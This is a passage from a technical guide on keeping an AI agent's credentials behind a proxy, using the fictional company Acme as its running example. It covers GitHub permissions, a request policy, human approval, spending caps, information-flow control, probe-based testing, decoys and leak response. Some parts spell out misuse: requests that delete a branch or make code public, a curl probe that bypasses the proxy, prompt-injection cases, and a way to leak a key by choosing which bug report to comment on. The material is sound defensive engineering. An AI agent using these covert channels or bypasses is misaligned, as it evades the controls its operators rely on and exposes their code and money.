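| Authorisation headers, cookies and custom headers | The names of the headers |
| Web address | Host and path, with the names of query parameters but not their values |
| Signed address | Host, and a note that the address was signed |
| Path that contains a secret, as with Telegram | The path with the placeholder in it |
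| Request and reply bodies | Their sizes |
| Upstream error message | Status code and the service's own request number |
| OAuth exchange | Which binding it used, whether it succeeded, and when the token expires |

The same rules should cover traces, the records of one request's path through several programs. Tracing software often saves complete web addresses automatically and sends them to another company for storage, so the intermediary has to remove secrets before it passes the data on. If a secret gets into a log or trace anyway, Acme should delete the entry and also replace the secret, because backups and search indexes may already contain copies.

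## Limiting what an agent can do with a secret it cannot read

Suppose that every protection so far works. Acme's agent can't read the GitHub token or the model key, the intermediary sends each secret only to its own service, and no reply reveals one. The agent can still make these requests:

```
DELETE https://api.github.com/repos/acme/shop/git/refs/heads/new-checkout

PATCH https://api.github.com/repos/acme/shop
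{"private": false}

POST https://api.anthropic.com/v1/messages
(through the gateway, 60 times a minute, all night)
```

The DELETE request removes a colleague's branch, a separate line of work on the code. A token with write access to the code can delete any branch except the repository's default one. The PATCH request makes the shop's private code public if the token can change the repository's settings, according to AprovanLabs' copy of GitHub's API description. The POST requests spend Acme's money. All of these requests come from the right sandbox and go to the right service.

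An agent can cause such damage without an attacker. *Secure Access Control for AI Agents* (Desai, 2026) describes how an agent deleted more than 200 emails from the inbox of an AI safety director at Meta, who had told it to wait for confirmation.

The intermediary is a confused deputy here because it adds authority to a request with no information about the request's purpose. It would receive the same DELETE request whether a developer had asked the agent to tidy up old branches or a stranger had written a bug report telling it to delete one. Acme therefore has to make most requests safe whatever their purpose, and ask a person about the rest. It should begin with controls that work even if the intermediary fails.

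### Permissions at GitHub

GitHub checks a token's permissions on every request, so a narrow token limits the damage even if someone steals it or takes over the proxy. Acme's app needs to write code, bug reports and pull requests, but it doesn't need the Administration permission, which covers a repository's settings, access, rules, visibility, transfer and deletion, according to damln's *Fine-grained repository permissions*. Without that permission, the PATCH request fails.

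For operators who use personal tokens instead of an app, GitHub's *Managing your personal access tokens* states that a token limited to one repository can still read every public repository on GitHub. That includes any repository where an attacker has left instructions. The same document describes an optional permission that lets a token make requests to Copilot, GitHub's AI assistant, and GitHub bills the account for requests beyond its allowance.

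Permissions can't prevent the DELETE request. According to GitHub's *REST API endpoints for Git references*, the permission to write a repository's contents covers creating, overwriting and deleting branches, so an agent that can push code can also delete it. Acme can close this gap with rulesets, which are GitHub's rules for particular branches, described in GitHub's *Available rules for rulesets*. Acme needs two:

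- On every branch except those whose names start with `agent/`, only Acme's developers can create, update or delete.
- On `main`, every change needs a pull request that a developer has approved, and nobody can bypass this.

The agent can then push only to its own branches and can't merge its work into `main`. Withholding the Administration permission also prevents the agent from editing the rulesets.

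These controls don't examine the code, so the agent can still put a back door in its own branch, and the reviewer might miss it. They also take time to maintain, since a task that needs a new permission fails until an administrator grants it. Rulesets on private repositories require a paid GitHub plan, and many smaller services offer only one key that can do everything.

### Separate identities for reading and writing

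Most of the agent's requests only read data. Acme's token program can therefore get two hourly tokens from GitHub, one read-only and one that can also write. The proxy attaches the writing token only when a request matches a rule for writing. If the proxy misclassifies a write as a read, GitHub refuses the request. The main extra work is keeping track of a second token.

GitHub applies a stricter version to agents on its automation service. *Safe Outputs* explains that the agent has no write permissions and instead produces a structured list of proposed changes, such as a new comment or pull request. Separate jobs check the list against the operator's settings, including a limit on each type of operation, and make the changes after the agent has finished. An agent under an attacker's control therefore can't write to the repository directly. The same restriction prevents an agent doing legitimate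 work from opening a pull request, seeing that the tests fail, and correcting its work in the same run.

The GitLost attack succeeded on this same service, and Aident's *How to Secure GitHub Agentic Workflows Against Prompt Injection* lists the agent's read access to other repositories as one of the causes. A separate job that posts a permitted comment will post private code if the comment contains it. Acme should therefore limit what the agent can read as carefully as what it can write, because an agent that can read only `acme/shop` can't leak another project's code.

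### A policy for the GitHub token

The proxy can apply finer rules than GitHub's permissions allow, because it sees each request's method, path, query and body. A simple policy in NVIDIA's documentation permits GET requests to GitHub's API and refuses PUT, POST and DELETE, which suits an agent that only needs to read. Loganathan's example for LangSmith attaches a GitHub token to any request under `/repos/`, whatever its method, so a DELETE request there would also get the token.

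Acme's agent has to write, so its policy lists each kind of request separately:

| Line | Request | Condition | Token |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | `GET /repos/acme/shop/issues` | Query contains only `state` and `page` | Read |
| 2 | `GET /repos/acme/shop/issues/{n}/comments` | Query contains only `page` | Read |
| 3 | `POST /repos/acme/shop/issues/{n}/comments` | One text field of up to 4,000 characters | Write |
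| 4 | `POST /repos/acme/shop/pulls` | From a branch under `agent/`, into `main` | Write |
| 5 | `DELETE /repos/acme/shop/git/refs/heads/agent/{name}` | A person approves | Write |
| 6 | `GET /acme/shop.git/info/refs` | Query names a download or a push | Read or write, to match |
| 7 | `POST /acme/shop.git/git-upload-pack` | None | Read |
| 8 | `POST /acme/shop.git/git-receive-pack` | Only branches under `agent/`, and no deletions | Write |
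| 9 | Anything else | Refuse | None |

Lines 1 to 5 apply to `api.github.com` and lines 6 to 8 to `github.com`.

Lines 1 and 2 let the agent read bug reports and their comments. The proxy accepts only digits for `{n}`, so the agent can't use that position to reach a different path.

Line 3 lets the agent comment. Line 4 lets it open a pull request, and its branch condition also excludes code from other people's copies of the repository. Line 5 lets it delete one of its own branches, only after someone agrees.

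Lines 6 to 8 are for Git. Every download or push starts with the request in line 6, and the query in that request shows which of the two will follow. Line 7 is a download even though it uses POST, so a policy that refused every POST request would stop the agent from fetching code.

Line 8 is a push. Its body begins with one entry for each branch, containing the old commit identifier, the new commit identifier, and the branch name. The proxy refuses the push if a name falls outside `agent/`, or if the new identifier is all zeros, which is how Git requests a deletion. Anthropic uses a similar check in the web version of Claude Code, where a proxy confirms that a push goes only to the configured branch before attaching the real token.

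Line 9 blocks any unlisted request, such as approving a pull request or creating a gist. It also blocks GitHub's other API, which uses a query language called GraphQL. Every GraphQL request is a POST to the same path, with the operation inside the body, so a rule about methods and paths can't distinguish reading a comment from deleting one. The proxy Desai describes, part of a product called Onyx Craft, reads the operation from the body. Acme blocks all GraphQL requests instead, which is simpler but will break some commands in GitHub's command-line tool.

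The proxy has to interpret each request the same way GitHub will, so it should standardise the path, just as it does the hostname, and forward exactly the version it checked. It should also remove headers such as `X-HTTP-Method-Override`, which can make some services treat a POST request as a DELETE.

Some products can't apply the whole policy by themselves. Vercel's firewall can match a request's method, path, query and headers, but for checks on the body, Tuttle suggests forwarding the request to a proxy that the customer runs.

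These rules prevent all the harmful GitHub requests at the start, but they can't filter out harmful text in a comment or harmful code in a push. They also have to be updated continually, because the agent will sometimes need to make a request that nobody predicted.

### Tokens that carry their own restrictions

A macaroon is a bearer credential with its restrictions, called caveats, written into it (Birgisson, Politz and colleagues, 2014, *Macaroons*). Anyone who holds a macaroon can add caveats, but nobody can remove them.

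GitHub's API doesn't accept macaroons, but suppose it did. GitHub would keep a secret root key and use HMAC, the keyed function in Amazon's request signatures, to build a chain:

```
s0 = HMAC(root key, "token 7f3a")
s1 = HMAC(s0, "repository = acme/shop")
s2 = HMAC(s1, "operation = read or comment")
s3 = HMAC(s2, "time < 17:00")
```

GitHub computes `s0` and `s1` and gives Acme a token that contains the identifier `token 7f3a`, the caveat about the repository, and `s1`. Acme adds the other two caveats without contacting GitHub. The finished token contains the identifier, the three caveats in readable text, and only the last signature, `s3`.

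When a request arrives, GitHub recalculates the chain from its root key, compares the result with `s3`, and checks that the request satisfies every caveat. A thief would need `s2` to delete the time limit, and nobody can compute `s2` from `s3`. Adding another caveat is easy because `s3` is the key for the next step.

A caveat can also require fresh proof from another service. Acme could add a caveat that requires a signed statement, valid for one minute, from its own approval system. GitHub could check the statement without any connection to that system.

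Macaroons are useful when an agent delegates part of its work, because it can give the other agent a weaker token than its own. The survey *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (Zhou and Zhang, 2026) includes a system called CAPMAS that does this. CAPMAS chooses each token's scope by comparing the meaning of the task with the available permissions. It may choose the wrong scope, but the agent that receives the token can't widen that scope.

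However, a caveat describes a permitted request, like a line in Acme's policy, so a token limited to commenting can still post private code in a comment. The main drawback is that the upstream service has to support macaroons, and few do. Only the service that issued a macaroon can check it, because checking requires the root key. Madden (2024) adds that macaroons have no formal standard and that their best-known library is quirky and not widely liked.

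Acme can avoid these problems when it both issues and checks the credential. For example, if the intermediary ran on a separate host, each sandbox would need a session token to identify itself, and Acme could make that token a macaroon. The shop agent could then give a helper agent a copy that permits only lines 1 and 2 of the policy and expires after ten minutes.

### Asking a person

A person can often supply what the intermediary lacks, which is knowledge of why someone wants the action. In Onyx Craft, an administrator decides whether each action always goes through, needs approval, or never goes through. Desai describes what happens when an action needs approval:

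1. The proxy holds the request before attaching any credential.
2. It shows the user the decoded contents. For an email, these are the recipients, the subject and the text.
3. The user approves the request once, approves such requests for the rest of the session, or rejects it.
4. If nobody answers in time, the proxy refuses the request.

Acme has too many requests that need approval to apply *SUDP*'s operation binding to all of them, but it can apply it to the few that a person sees. The proxy can store the request it displayed and send exactly that copy. Each approval should also expire quickly and work only once. Zhou and Zhang point out that circumstances can change between an approval and a delayed action, and that a retry can repeat an action that already succeeded.

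Human approval can stop a damaging request that every other rule permits, but only if reviewers pay attention. Suppose the agent makes 300 requests a day and a careful decision takes 20 seconds. Reviewing every request would take 100 minutes a day, and people would soon start approving requests without reading them. If only five requests a day need approval, reviewing them takes less than two minutes. Approving a whole session at once also saves time, but it lets later requests through without review.

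Acme's policy therefore requires a person's approval only for deletions, and developers also review each pull request before merging it. Nobody is available to approve requests from an agent that runs at night. For scheduled tasks, Onyx Craft lets people approve named apps in advance, and those approvals apply only while the task is running.

### Limits on rate, size and spending

None of these controls prevents the agent from wasting money, because each call to the model is a permitted request. Suppose the gateway allows 60 requests a minute and each costs $0.05:

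```
60 requests a minute × $0.05 = $3 a minute
$50 a day ÷ $3 a minute      = 16.7 minutes
```

A faulty loop that ran for eight hours would cost $1,440 without a cap. With a cap of $50 a day, the gateway rejects further requests after about 17 minutes, limiting the loss to $50. The agent then can't work until the next day, so an attacker who can't steal anything can still disable it by using up the cap. Lowering the rate to 10 requests a minute wouldn't reduce the maximum loss, but it would give Acme 100 minutes to notice the problem before the agent reaches the cap.

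The cap holds only if the gateway counts correctly. Model providers charge by the amount of text, so some requests cost far more than $0.05. The gateway should limit the length of each answer, work out the most that a request could cost, and subtract that amount from the remaining budget before sending the request. If it subtracted the cost afterwards, many requests sent at once could all pass before the total changed. The gateway should also count spending over the previous 24 hours, because a cap that resets at midnight allows $50 just before midnight and another $50 just after.

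Acme should also keep the spending limit at the model provider, since the gateway's cap doesn't apply to a stolen key. On GitHub, a limit of 10 comments an hour would stop the agent from flooding the project, although legitimate work might also reach the limit on a busy day.

### How data leaves through permitted requests

Any service that stores text can carry data to anyone who can later read it. The data can be put in a comment, but also in a branch name or the title of a pull request. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) makes the same point about email, where an agent allowed to send messages can hide private data in a plausible one.

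Limits on size and rate work against bulk copying. If the shop's code is 50 MB, copying it into comments of 4,000 characters would take 12,500 comments, or 52 days at 10 comments an hour.

Limits on comment length don't help with a short secret. Amazon's secret access keys, for example, are 40 characters long, and one might be in the shop's code. It would fit in an ordinary comment, and a limit below 40 characters would make comments useless. Even then, the agent could post the key one character at a time.

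The agent could also send the key without writing any part of it. If the project has 32 open bug reports, choosing which one to comment on conveys five bits, because 32 is 2 to the power of 5. A random key of 40 letters and digits contains about 238 bits, so the agent could send all of it in 48 harmless comments by choosing each report to match the next five bits.

The risk therefore depends mostly on who can read the places where the agent writes. Only people at Acme can read `acme/shop`, and they can already see its code, so a comment there reveals nothing new to them. That would change if Acme connected the repository to an outside chat service, published a preview website from every branch, or used the same agent on one of its public projects.

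### Whether request rules are enough

Some researchers argue that checking requests one by one can't solve this problem. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) describes access control as a gate that can only allow or deny access, and recommends adding information-flow control, which tracks data through the system after the agent has read it.

Information-flow control attaches labels to data. *SPA* (2026), which applies the method to agents that keep information between tasks, distinguishes two kinds. Confidentiality labels record how sensitive data is, so that private code can't end up in a public comment. Integrity labels record how trustworthy the data is, so that a stranger's text can't determine where an email is sent.

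The best-known design for agents is CaMeL, which Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues published in 2025. Suppose a developer asks the agent to summarise the newest bug report in a comment. *CaMeLoT* (2026), which builds on CaMeL, explains how the system would handle such a task:

1. One model reads only the developer's request and writes a short program that fetches the report, summarises it and posts the result.
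2. A second model, which has no tools, reads the report and writes the summary.
3. The software that runs the program labels every value with its sources and with the people who may read it.
4. Before each tool call, the software checks those labels against a policy.

If the bug report contains an instruction to publish the shop's code, only the second model reads it, and that model can't call tools, so the instruction may distort the summary but can't add a step to the program.

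This approach has done well in tests. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) reports that CaMeL stopped nearly all the attacks in AgentDojo, a standard test of prompt injection, with little change in the number of tasks completed. *APPA* (2026) describes a newer system in which no attack succeeded in 1,320 protected runs. If those runs were a random sample of attacks, the true success rate would probably be below about 0.2%, but real attackers adapt to the defence they face. The system scored between 64.2% and 91% on completing useful work, so the protection may make it less useful for some jobs.

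Part of the problem is label creep, in which everything that touches sensitive data is labelled sensitive too, until the policy blocks ordinary work. In *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026) simulated groups of agents working on tasks of 20 tool calls each. When 4 of the 20 calls involved sensitive data, the share of calls labelled sensitive was about 5 percentage points higher if all messages went through a central agent than if agents communicated directly. Giving the sensitive tools to only a few agents reduced label creep. Using more agents also reduced it, but created more connections to monitor.

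Gregory and colleagues conclude that good design can't fully prevent label creep and that systems need a safe way to remove labels. Their simulation assumes that agents never forget anything and that labels never come off, so labels were bound to accumulate. It also didn't use a language model. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), which extends CaMeL to groups of agents, predicts that the loss of useful work will shrink as models get better at planning and writing code.

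Acme's agent also has a shell, which makes CaMeL's approach harder to apply. CaMeL can track each value only if every step goes through its own software. A script the agent writes can read the whole repository and mix it with anything else in the sandbox, and a malicious package can send requests without involving the model. The labels would have to be kept outside the sandbox, and any output from the sandbox would need the strictest label of anything inside it.

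The proxy can enforce that coarse version with an ordinary rule. Once a sandbox has read a private repository, the proxy blocks it from writing anywhere public until Acme deletes the sandbox. This rule would have stopped GitLost, and enforcing it requires no information about the model's reasoning. It also blocks harmless public comments, so Acme would need a separate agent for its public projects.

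For the shop agent, request rules are enough to protect the code's confidentiality on GitHub, as long as outsiders can't read anything the agent writes there. An agent that must read private data and write to outsiders in the same task needs information-flow control or a person to check each message. Neither approach removes the risk of a back door. A strict integrity rule would stop a stranger's bug report from influencing the shop's code, but the agent's job is to fix reported bugs, so Acme still depends on the developer who reviews the pull request.

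## Testing the intermediary and keeping it secure in use

Acme's rules protect its secrets only if the running system enforces them. *Sandman* (2026), which describes a service that runs sandboxes for training AI models, reports a live check of six sandboxes labelled as having no outbound access. All six could reach the internet, because only a modified version of the software that creates sandboxes installed the block. The service now applies the label only if it also installs the block.

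Acme should therefore attack its own intermediary from inside the sandbox before any agent uses it, and again whenever something changes.

### Preparing the test

The full test runs on a copy of the system, built from the same images and rule files with a few additions. An empty private repository called `acme/shop-test` replaces `acme/shop`. The gateway holds a separate model key, and its daily cap is $1. Acme also runs a small web server that records every request and returns whatever response the tester chooses. The server has two names, `bound.acme.example` and `open.acme.example`. The proxy can reach both, but only the first has a binding, which attaches a made-up secret.

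The test uses dummy secrets because a successful probe leaks the secret it finds, perhaps into a transcript or the model provider's records. Dummy secrets also make the search more exact, because Acme can search for their precise values and encoded forms. Kenney and colleagues searched for the patterns of common token formats, which can miss an unfamiliar one. The search should run outside the sandbox on data copied out of it, because a script inside the sandbox that contained the secrets would show up as a match.

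Three calls from inside the sandbox form the core of the test:

```
check='curl -s -o /dev/null -w %{http_code}'

$check https://api.github.com/repos/acme/shop-test/issues   # must print 200
$check https://open.acme.example/                           # must print 200
$check --noproxy '*' https://api.github.com/                # must print 000
```

The first call is a positive control, meaning it must succeed. The second must reach Acme's server without a secret, and the server's record shows whether it did. The third is an attempt to bypass the proxy, and 000 means it got no answer.

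Suppose Acme left out the positive control and ran its probes in a sandbox with no network. Direct connections would fail, and no outside server would receive a secret because the sandbox couldn't send anything. A search of the sandbox would find no secrets. The system would pass all these checks, but Acme would not have shown that the intermediary could keep a secret safe while using it.

The positive control must also be a call that fails without the secret. GitHub hides private repositories from anonymous callers, so a successful reply from `acme/shop-test` shows that the proxy attached a working token. A request to a public repository would succeed even without a token. E2B, which hosts sandboxes for agents, warns in its manual that checking whether a secret exists doesn't test whether E2B's proxy can attach it. If the proxy fails to attach the secret, the only sign may be an authentication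 error from the upstream service.

### A probe for each threat

The tester writes down every expected result before starting, because an unexpected result is easy to explain away afterwards. Each probe also has its own positive control, to show that the probe could have detected a failure.

| Threat | Probe | Expected result | Positive control |
|---|---|---|---|
| Agent reads the secret in storage | As root, copy out the environment, files and process memory, then search them for the dummy secrets | No match | The search finds a harmless marker hidden in the sandbox |
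| Agent goes around the intermediary | Try direct connections over IPv4 and IPv6, a DNS lookup, a `ping` and the cloud metadata address | No answer | The ordinary connections work from a machine with internet access |
| Intermediary sends the secret to an unapproved destination | Call `open.acme.example` and lookalikes of GitHub's address, and have `bound` redirect to `open` | No secret arrives at `open` or a lookalike | The dummy secret arrives at `bound` |
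| Another caller uses the intermediary | Connect from the second team's sandbox, then add a link and try again | No connection, then a refusal | The shop agent's sandbox gets an answer |
| Secret comes back in a response or log | Have `bound` repeat the secret in a header, a compressed reply and a partial reply, then search the logs | The proxy masks the secret or refuses the reply, and the logs don't contain it | A harmless reply arrives unchanged |
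| Agent misuses authority without reading the secret | Delete a colleague's branch, push to `main`, post a comment of 4,001 characters and send a GraphQL request | The proxy refuses, and GitHub receives nothing | A comment of 4,000 characters and a push to `agent/test` succeed |
| Attacker changes the control plane | As root, write to every mounted folder and try to open the administration and Docker sockets | The rules don't change, and neither socket answers | An administrator's change takes effect |
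| Agent exhausts money or service | Send 40 model requests at once, each with a maximum cost of $0.05 | No more than 20 reach the provider | One request sent beforehand succeeds |

A refusal isn't enough to pass the misuse probe, because a faulty proxy could forward a request and then report that it had refused it. *One Policy, Four Interception Points* (2026) presents a test suite for rules about agents' actions. The suite records the traffic instead of relying on each component's account, and it reports an incomplete result if it hasn't measured every required route. Acme should do the same, so that nobody counts a probe that never ran as a pass.

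*Distributing Security Controls Through Harness Engineering* (2026) also allows a mixed result, often for an attack that did some harm without fully succeeding. If Acme's proxy blocked a deletion but included the token in its error message, the result would be mixed, and Acme should treat it as a failure.

The tester should also send the harmful GitHub requests directly to GitHub with the test token, from a machine outside the sandbox. This shows which requests GitHub would still block if the proxy failed.

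### Sixteen probes by Kenney and colleagues

Kenney and colleagues ran a similar test on September 27, 2026. They set a yes-or-no expectation for each probe in advance and used one connector in each of two experiments.

The first experiment used the connector for FRED, the economic data service. Code in the sandbox searched its environment variables, 12 common locations for credentials and the folders where platforms usually place secrets. It then tried Amazon's and Google's metadata endpoints and called FRED, three echo services and two unrelated APIs.

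The second experiment used a GitHub connector. The code requested the identity of the account it was using, inspected the headers of a request it had prepared, and searched its environment variables again. It also called two echo services and one unrelated API that requires a key.

The experiments produced 16 scored probes in seven control domains. Five probes tested whether the intermediary attached a credential only for the right host, and one tested whether an authorised call worked. The other ten were split evenly among environment variables, files, calls to other services, the code's view of the credential, and cloud metadata.

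All 16 gave the expected result. GitHub returned the account's identity even though the code had supplied no credential. None of the sandbox's 20 environment variables contained a recognisable secret, and none of the 12 locations existed. OpenAI's API reported missing authentication in both experiments. Both metadata requests timed out after six seconds.

The FRED call failed because the connector put the key in the wrong part of the request. Kenney and colleagues scored this as a functional fault, separately from security. The failure also left the first experiment without a working positive control for the secret. Its searches would have found nothing even if the connector had held no key, so the evidence comes mainly from the GitHub experiment.

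The number of probes is small too. If a fraction *p* of all possible probes would fail, the chance that a random sample of 16 would all pass is (1 − *p*) to the power of 16:

```
(1 − 0.17)^16 ≈ 0.05
```

At 95% confidence, 16 passes with no failures rule out only failure rates above about 17%, because about one in 20 samples of that size would show no failures even if the failure rate were 17%. Lowering that limit to 1% would take 299 passes with no failures.

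Kenney and colleagues, who built the product, chose the 16 probes, so these weren't a random sample either. They say the sample can't be used to estimate how common failures are. An attacker also doesn't pick methods at random and needs only one that works.

Jin and colleagues found no unauthorised use in their trials and calculated an upper limit of 3.7% for the true rate. The trials used fixed, scripted scenarios, so the limit applies only to those. Repeating them would not show how the intermediary handles other attacks.

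Kenney and colleagues list several things they didn't test:

- redirects from an approved service to another address
- DNS rebinding, in which a domain's owner changes its address after the intermediary has checked it
- capture of new tokens during an OAuth refresh
- an attacker who controls an approved service
- many requests at the same time

They also didn't verify the isolation between customers, the completeness of the logs or the controls on administrators. No probe tried to misuse GitHub's authority, change the rules or run up a bill. Acme can test redirects and a hostile approved service with its own recording server, and rebinding with a domain it controls.

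### Why passing every test isn't enough

*Contain, Conform, Compare (Extended Version)* (Nguyen, 2026) describes a container for running code that AI agents write. The first three versions withstood all their scripted attacks, which numbered 52, 60 and 98. AI agents separate from those that had built the container then attacked each version and found nine serious holes in total. The seventh and last version withstood 200 scripted attacks, and the attacking agents found no serious holes in it.

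All nine holes involved something the container shared with its host, such as files that the host processed after the agent had changed them. None of the attacks broke out of the container itself. In the version that passed 98 attacks, the model server would fetch web addresses named in a request. Acme's gateway could have a similar problem if its model provider fetches images or pages for customers, because an agent could leak private code by putting it in the address. Acme should test this by sending a request that names the address of its recording server. If the provider fetches that address, Acme should block such requests at the gateway.

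Somebody who didn't build Acme's intermediary should attack it too, and every hole they find should become a new probe.

### An audit of nine healthcare agents

In *Caging the Agents*, Saikat Maiti reports on nine agents at a healthcare technology company over what the paper calls a 90-day deployment. On March 11, 2026, an auditing agent searched their machines and found four high-severity exposures:

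- One agent's `.bashrc`, a file of commands that run when a shell opens, contained 12 API keys, including a GitHub token and credentials for Amazon's model service.
- The same agent's main configuration file, which held all its stored credentials, was readable by every account on the machine.
- A second agent's configuration file had the same fault.
- A third agent's `.bashrc` contained a key for Amazon's model service.

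The auditing agent fixed all four that day by removing the keys from the shell files and tightening the permissions on the configuration files. Six of the nine machines had no finding above low severity, but four medium-severity findings about `.env` files remained open. The auditing agent saved backups of the shell files, which probably still contained the keys, and the paper doesn't report that anyone replaced them. Stricter permissions don't stop an agent from reading its own account's files.

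The audit is good evidence that credentials accumulate where agents can read them, but much weaker evidence that an intermediary solves the problem. The paper's abstract presents the whole architecture as deployed, but a later section lists the sidecars that would hold the credentials as part of a "current migration target". The newest machines that the paper describes as running still kept credentials in `.env` files. The dates it gives cover only 36 days, from February 3 to March 11.

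Two parts of the planned design need testing before anyone relies on it. Each sidecar shares a pod, and therefore a network policy, with its agent, and the auditing agent's allowlist includes Google's metadata endpoint. Maiti recognises that the auditing agent is the most valuable target in the fleet, since it can log in to all nine machines, and suggests studying non-agent scanners. Searching files for secrets doesn't require a language model, so Acme should use an ordinary program.

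### Repeating the tests

Acme's launcher runs a short version of the test each time it starts a microVM. *Parallax* (2026) describes a system with the same safeguard. Before any call to a model, its agent process tries to read and write files on the host, open a forbidden connection and reach the program that supervises it. If any attempt succeeds, the system does not start.

In *Permission Denied*, Davidovich, Amar and colleagues (2026) benchmark coding agents under security restrictions. They also probe for common bypasses, such as nested shells and unusual ports, and check that permitted actions still work. If a probe fails, they discard the sandbox and start a new one. They delete the probes' files before the agent begins.

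Acme runs the full test after any update, rule change or server restart. After a restart, it also tests sandboxes that were already open, because the loss of Docker's ICMP block affected only those.

To test rule changes, Acme can keep a file of recorded requests with the decision it expects for each. *One Policy, Four Interception Points* replays such cases through every route and compares the decisions. At Acme, this would reveal a new rule that blocks deleting a branch through GitHub's API but allows it through `git push`.

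The tests should include ordinary work too, because people tend to loosen rules that get in their way. Davidovich and colleagues gave 12 agents the same 89 tasks with and without strict limits on network access, files and privileges. Under the limits, every agent's completion rate fell, by 7.1 to 18.3 percentage points, and the average cost of a task rose by 16.0% to 167.3%. The limits caused some of the failures directly, because they made seven of the tasks impossible. After tightening its own rules, Acme should check whether tasks still succeed and whether its model bill has risen.

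### What the log must record

The earlier rules on redaction say what the log must leave out. It must still contain enough to answer three questions after an incident: who made the request, why the intermediary allowed it, and whether a secret left with it. Acme writes two entries for each request:

```
{"id": "r-48213", "time": "09:14:02.118Z", "sandbox": "shop-agent-17",
 "request": "POST api.github.com/repos/acme/shop/issues/52/comments",
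 "rules": "version 31", "line": 3, "decision": "allow", "approved_by": null}

{"id": "r-48213", "time": "09:14:02.391Z", "secret_attached": true,
 "secret": "github-write", "secret_version": 212, "header": "Authorization",
 "sent_to": "api.github.com", "status": 201}
```

The proxy writes two log entries for each request. It writes the first before it attaches the token, and refuses the request if it can't write to the log. The second records the outcome. If the second entry is missing, perhaps because the proxy crashed, investigators should assume that the token left the proxy.

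The `secret_attached` field matters most in a suspected leak. SC Media notes that Docker's log lacked this information when its proxy could send keys to unapproved servers, so the activity looked legitimate. Recording it is easy. The example proxy in ZenML's tutorial *Credential proxy* prints the name of each header it adds and the destination host.

An intruder may try to edit the log. Jin and colleagues' prototype makes this detectable by linking the entries with hashes, which are short codes calculated from the data. In a simple chain of this kind, each entry includes the previous entry's hash, so an entry that has been changed no longer matches the hash stored in the next one. Ghifiardi (2026) used such a chain in *Optional Traps* but points out that anyone who can replace the whole log can recalculate every hash. Acme should therefore send each entry immediately to another machine, where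 the intermediary can add entries but can't change them.

Acme should also compare the intermediary's log with GitHub's. Only the intermediary should use the GitHub token, so any use that appears in GitHub's log but not in the intermediary's suggests that someone has stolen it. Datadog Security Labs describes a campaign in which attackers used stolen GitHub tokens to explore companies' private repositories. Most attempts to copy data failed, but in one case GitHub's audit log recorded an attacker's program cloning a private repository, which an intermediary's log would not show.

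### Decoy credentials

A decoy credential is a fake secret that triggers an alert when somebody uses it. It suits a sandbox with an intermediary because the sandbox shouldn't contain any real credentials that a program could have a good reason to use.

Ghifiardi tested what decoys add to other protections. The target was a mock web service with a debugging page that leaked its real key, and the attacker was an agent running a small language model. The agent attacked the service 20 times under each of three conditions:

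| Debugging page | Sessions in which the agent stole records | Sessions in which the service cut off the agent |
|---|---|---|
| Leaks the real key | 20 | 0 |
| Removed | 0 | 0 |
| Shows a decoy key | 0 | 19 |

Removing the real key stopped the thefts, and the decoy made it possible to identify and block the attacker. Ghifiardi calculates that, with only 20 sessions, the true theft rate could still be as high as 16.1% under either protection. The agent also knew where to look, which made both the leak and the decoy easier to find.

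In an earlier trial, another small model ignored decoys placed elsewhere in the service and went straight to the real key. Acme should therefore put decoys where an attacker would expect real secrets, such as in environment variables and a `.env` file. Each place should have a different decoy, so that an alert shows where the leak began.

Legitimate agents can also trigger alerts. In one of Ghifiardi's trials, an agent that already had the correct key found the decoy, used it instead and lost its access. Ghifiardi recommends a limited, reversible response, such as blocking one client for 15 minutes. At Acme, an alert should pause the sandbox until a person has investigated. *Say Shibboleth* (2026) notes that attacking agents can recognise decoy systems and avoid them, so a lack of alerts is only weak evidence that there has been no attack.

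The type of decoy determines where Acme can detect its use. A fake GitHub token triggers an alert if someone sends it through Acme's proxy, but GitHub won't tell Acme about a failed login from elsewhere. If the decoy is an Amazon key for an empty, monitored account, Acme can detect its use anywhere.

Decoys can also reveal leaks outside Acme's systems. *Researchers fed AI 2 million secrets. Strangers used them* (BagheeraAltered, 2026) summarises a study in which the security company Dragos put unique web addresses and decoy credentials in about two million prompts to AI services. Outsiders later visited the addresses and used the decoy Amazon credentials. So if somebody uses one of Acme's decoys, it may have leaked at a model provider after the agent read it.

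### Practising rotation

Rotation means replacing a secret and revoking the old one. Acme should practise it before an emergency, using its existing steps for planned and urgent replacement. Kenney and colleagues recommend recording the owner, permissions, expiry date and replacement method of every credential. They also recommend testing what happens when a token expires, an employee leaves or an administrator disables a connector.

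Twice a year, Acme picks a secret for a replacement drill without warning its owner, and measures the time until the upstream service refuses the old value. Acme revokes the secret while an agent is working, to check that the intermediary reports an error instead of falling back on another secret. Like any planned replacement, the drill ends with a test that the old secret no longer works.

### When a secret may have leaked

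Leaks can occur without an attacker. Positive Technologies' *PT-2026-44905 · Github · Github Cli* describes a flaw in GitHub's command-line tool, which before version 2.93.0 sent users' tokens to other companies' servers in normal use. This happened partly because the tool treated every address ending in `.github.com` as GitHub's main site. The entry advises users to update the tool, revoke their tokens and review their logs. In Acme's sandbox, the tool would have sent only a placeholder.

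When Acme suspects a leak, it should work in this order:

1. Revoke the secret at the upstream service, along with any short-lived tokens made from it.
2. Disconnect the sandbox, but keep its disk and memory for investigators.
3. Save the logs of the intermediary, the exit filter and the upstream service.
4. Find out how the secret left, and close that route.
5. Create a new secret and load it into a clean copy of the intermediary.
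6. Search the upstream logs for everything that anyone did with the old secret since the earliest possible time of the leak, and undo any damage.
7. Add a probe that repeats the leak, run the full test, and reconnect the agent.

Acme revokes the secret first because a thief could otherwise keep using it during the investigation. Acme should not issue the new secret before step 5, or it could leak by the same route. If the intermediary itself may be compromised, Acme should also replace every other secret it held. If the logs can't show whether a secret leaked, Acme should assume that it did. If an agent misused its authority without learning the secret, Acme can skip revoking and replacing it.

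### The eight threats after protection and testing

Acme can now complete the table from its threat model. The last column lists the risks that its owners have to accept or reduce by other means.

| Threat | Protection | Test | Residual risk |
|---|---|---|---|
| Agent reads the secret in storage | Secrets stay outside the microVM, under separate accounts | Search the sandbox for dummy secrets | A flaw in the hypervisor or in a program that serves the sandbox |
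| Agent goes around the intermediary | The microVM has no network card and no old logins | Try direct connections at every start | Someone puts a working credential in the code or the agent's session |
| Intermediary sends the secret to an unapproved destination | Exact bindings, no followed redirects, and an exit filter | Call servers that have no binding | An attacker who controls the approved service already receives the secret |
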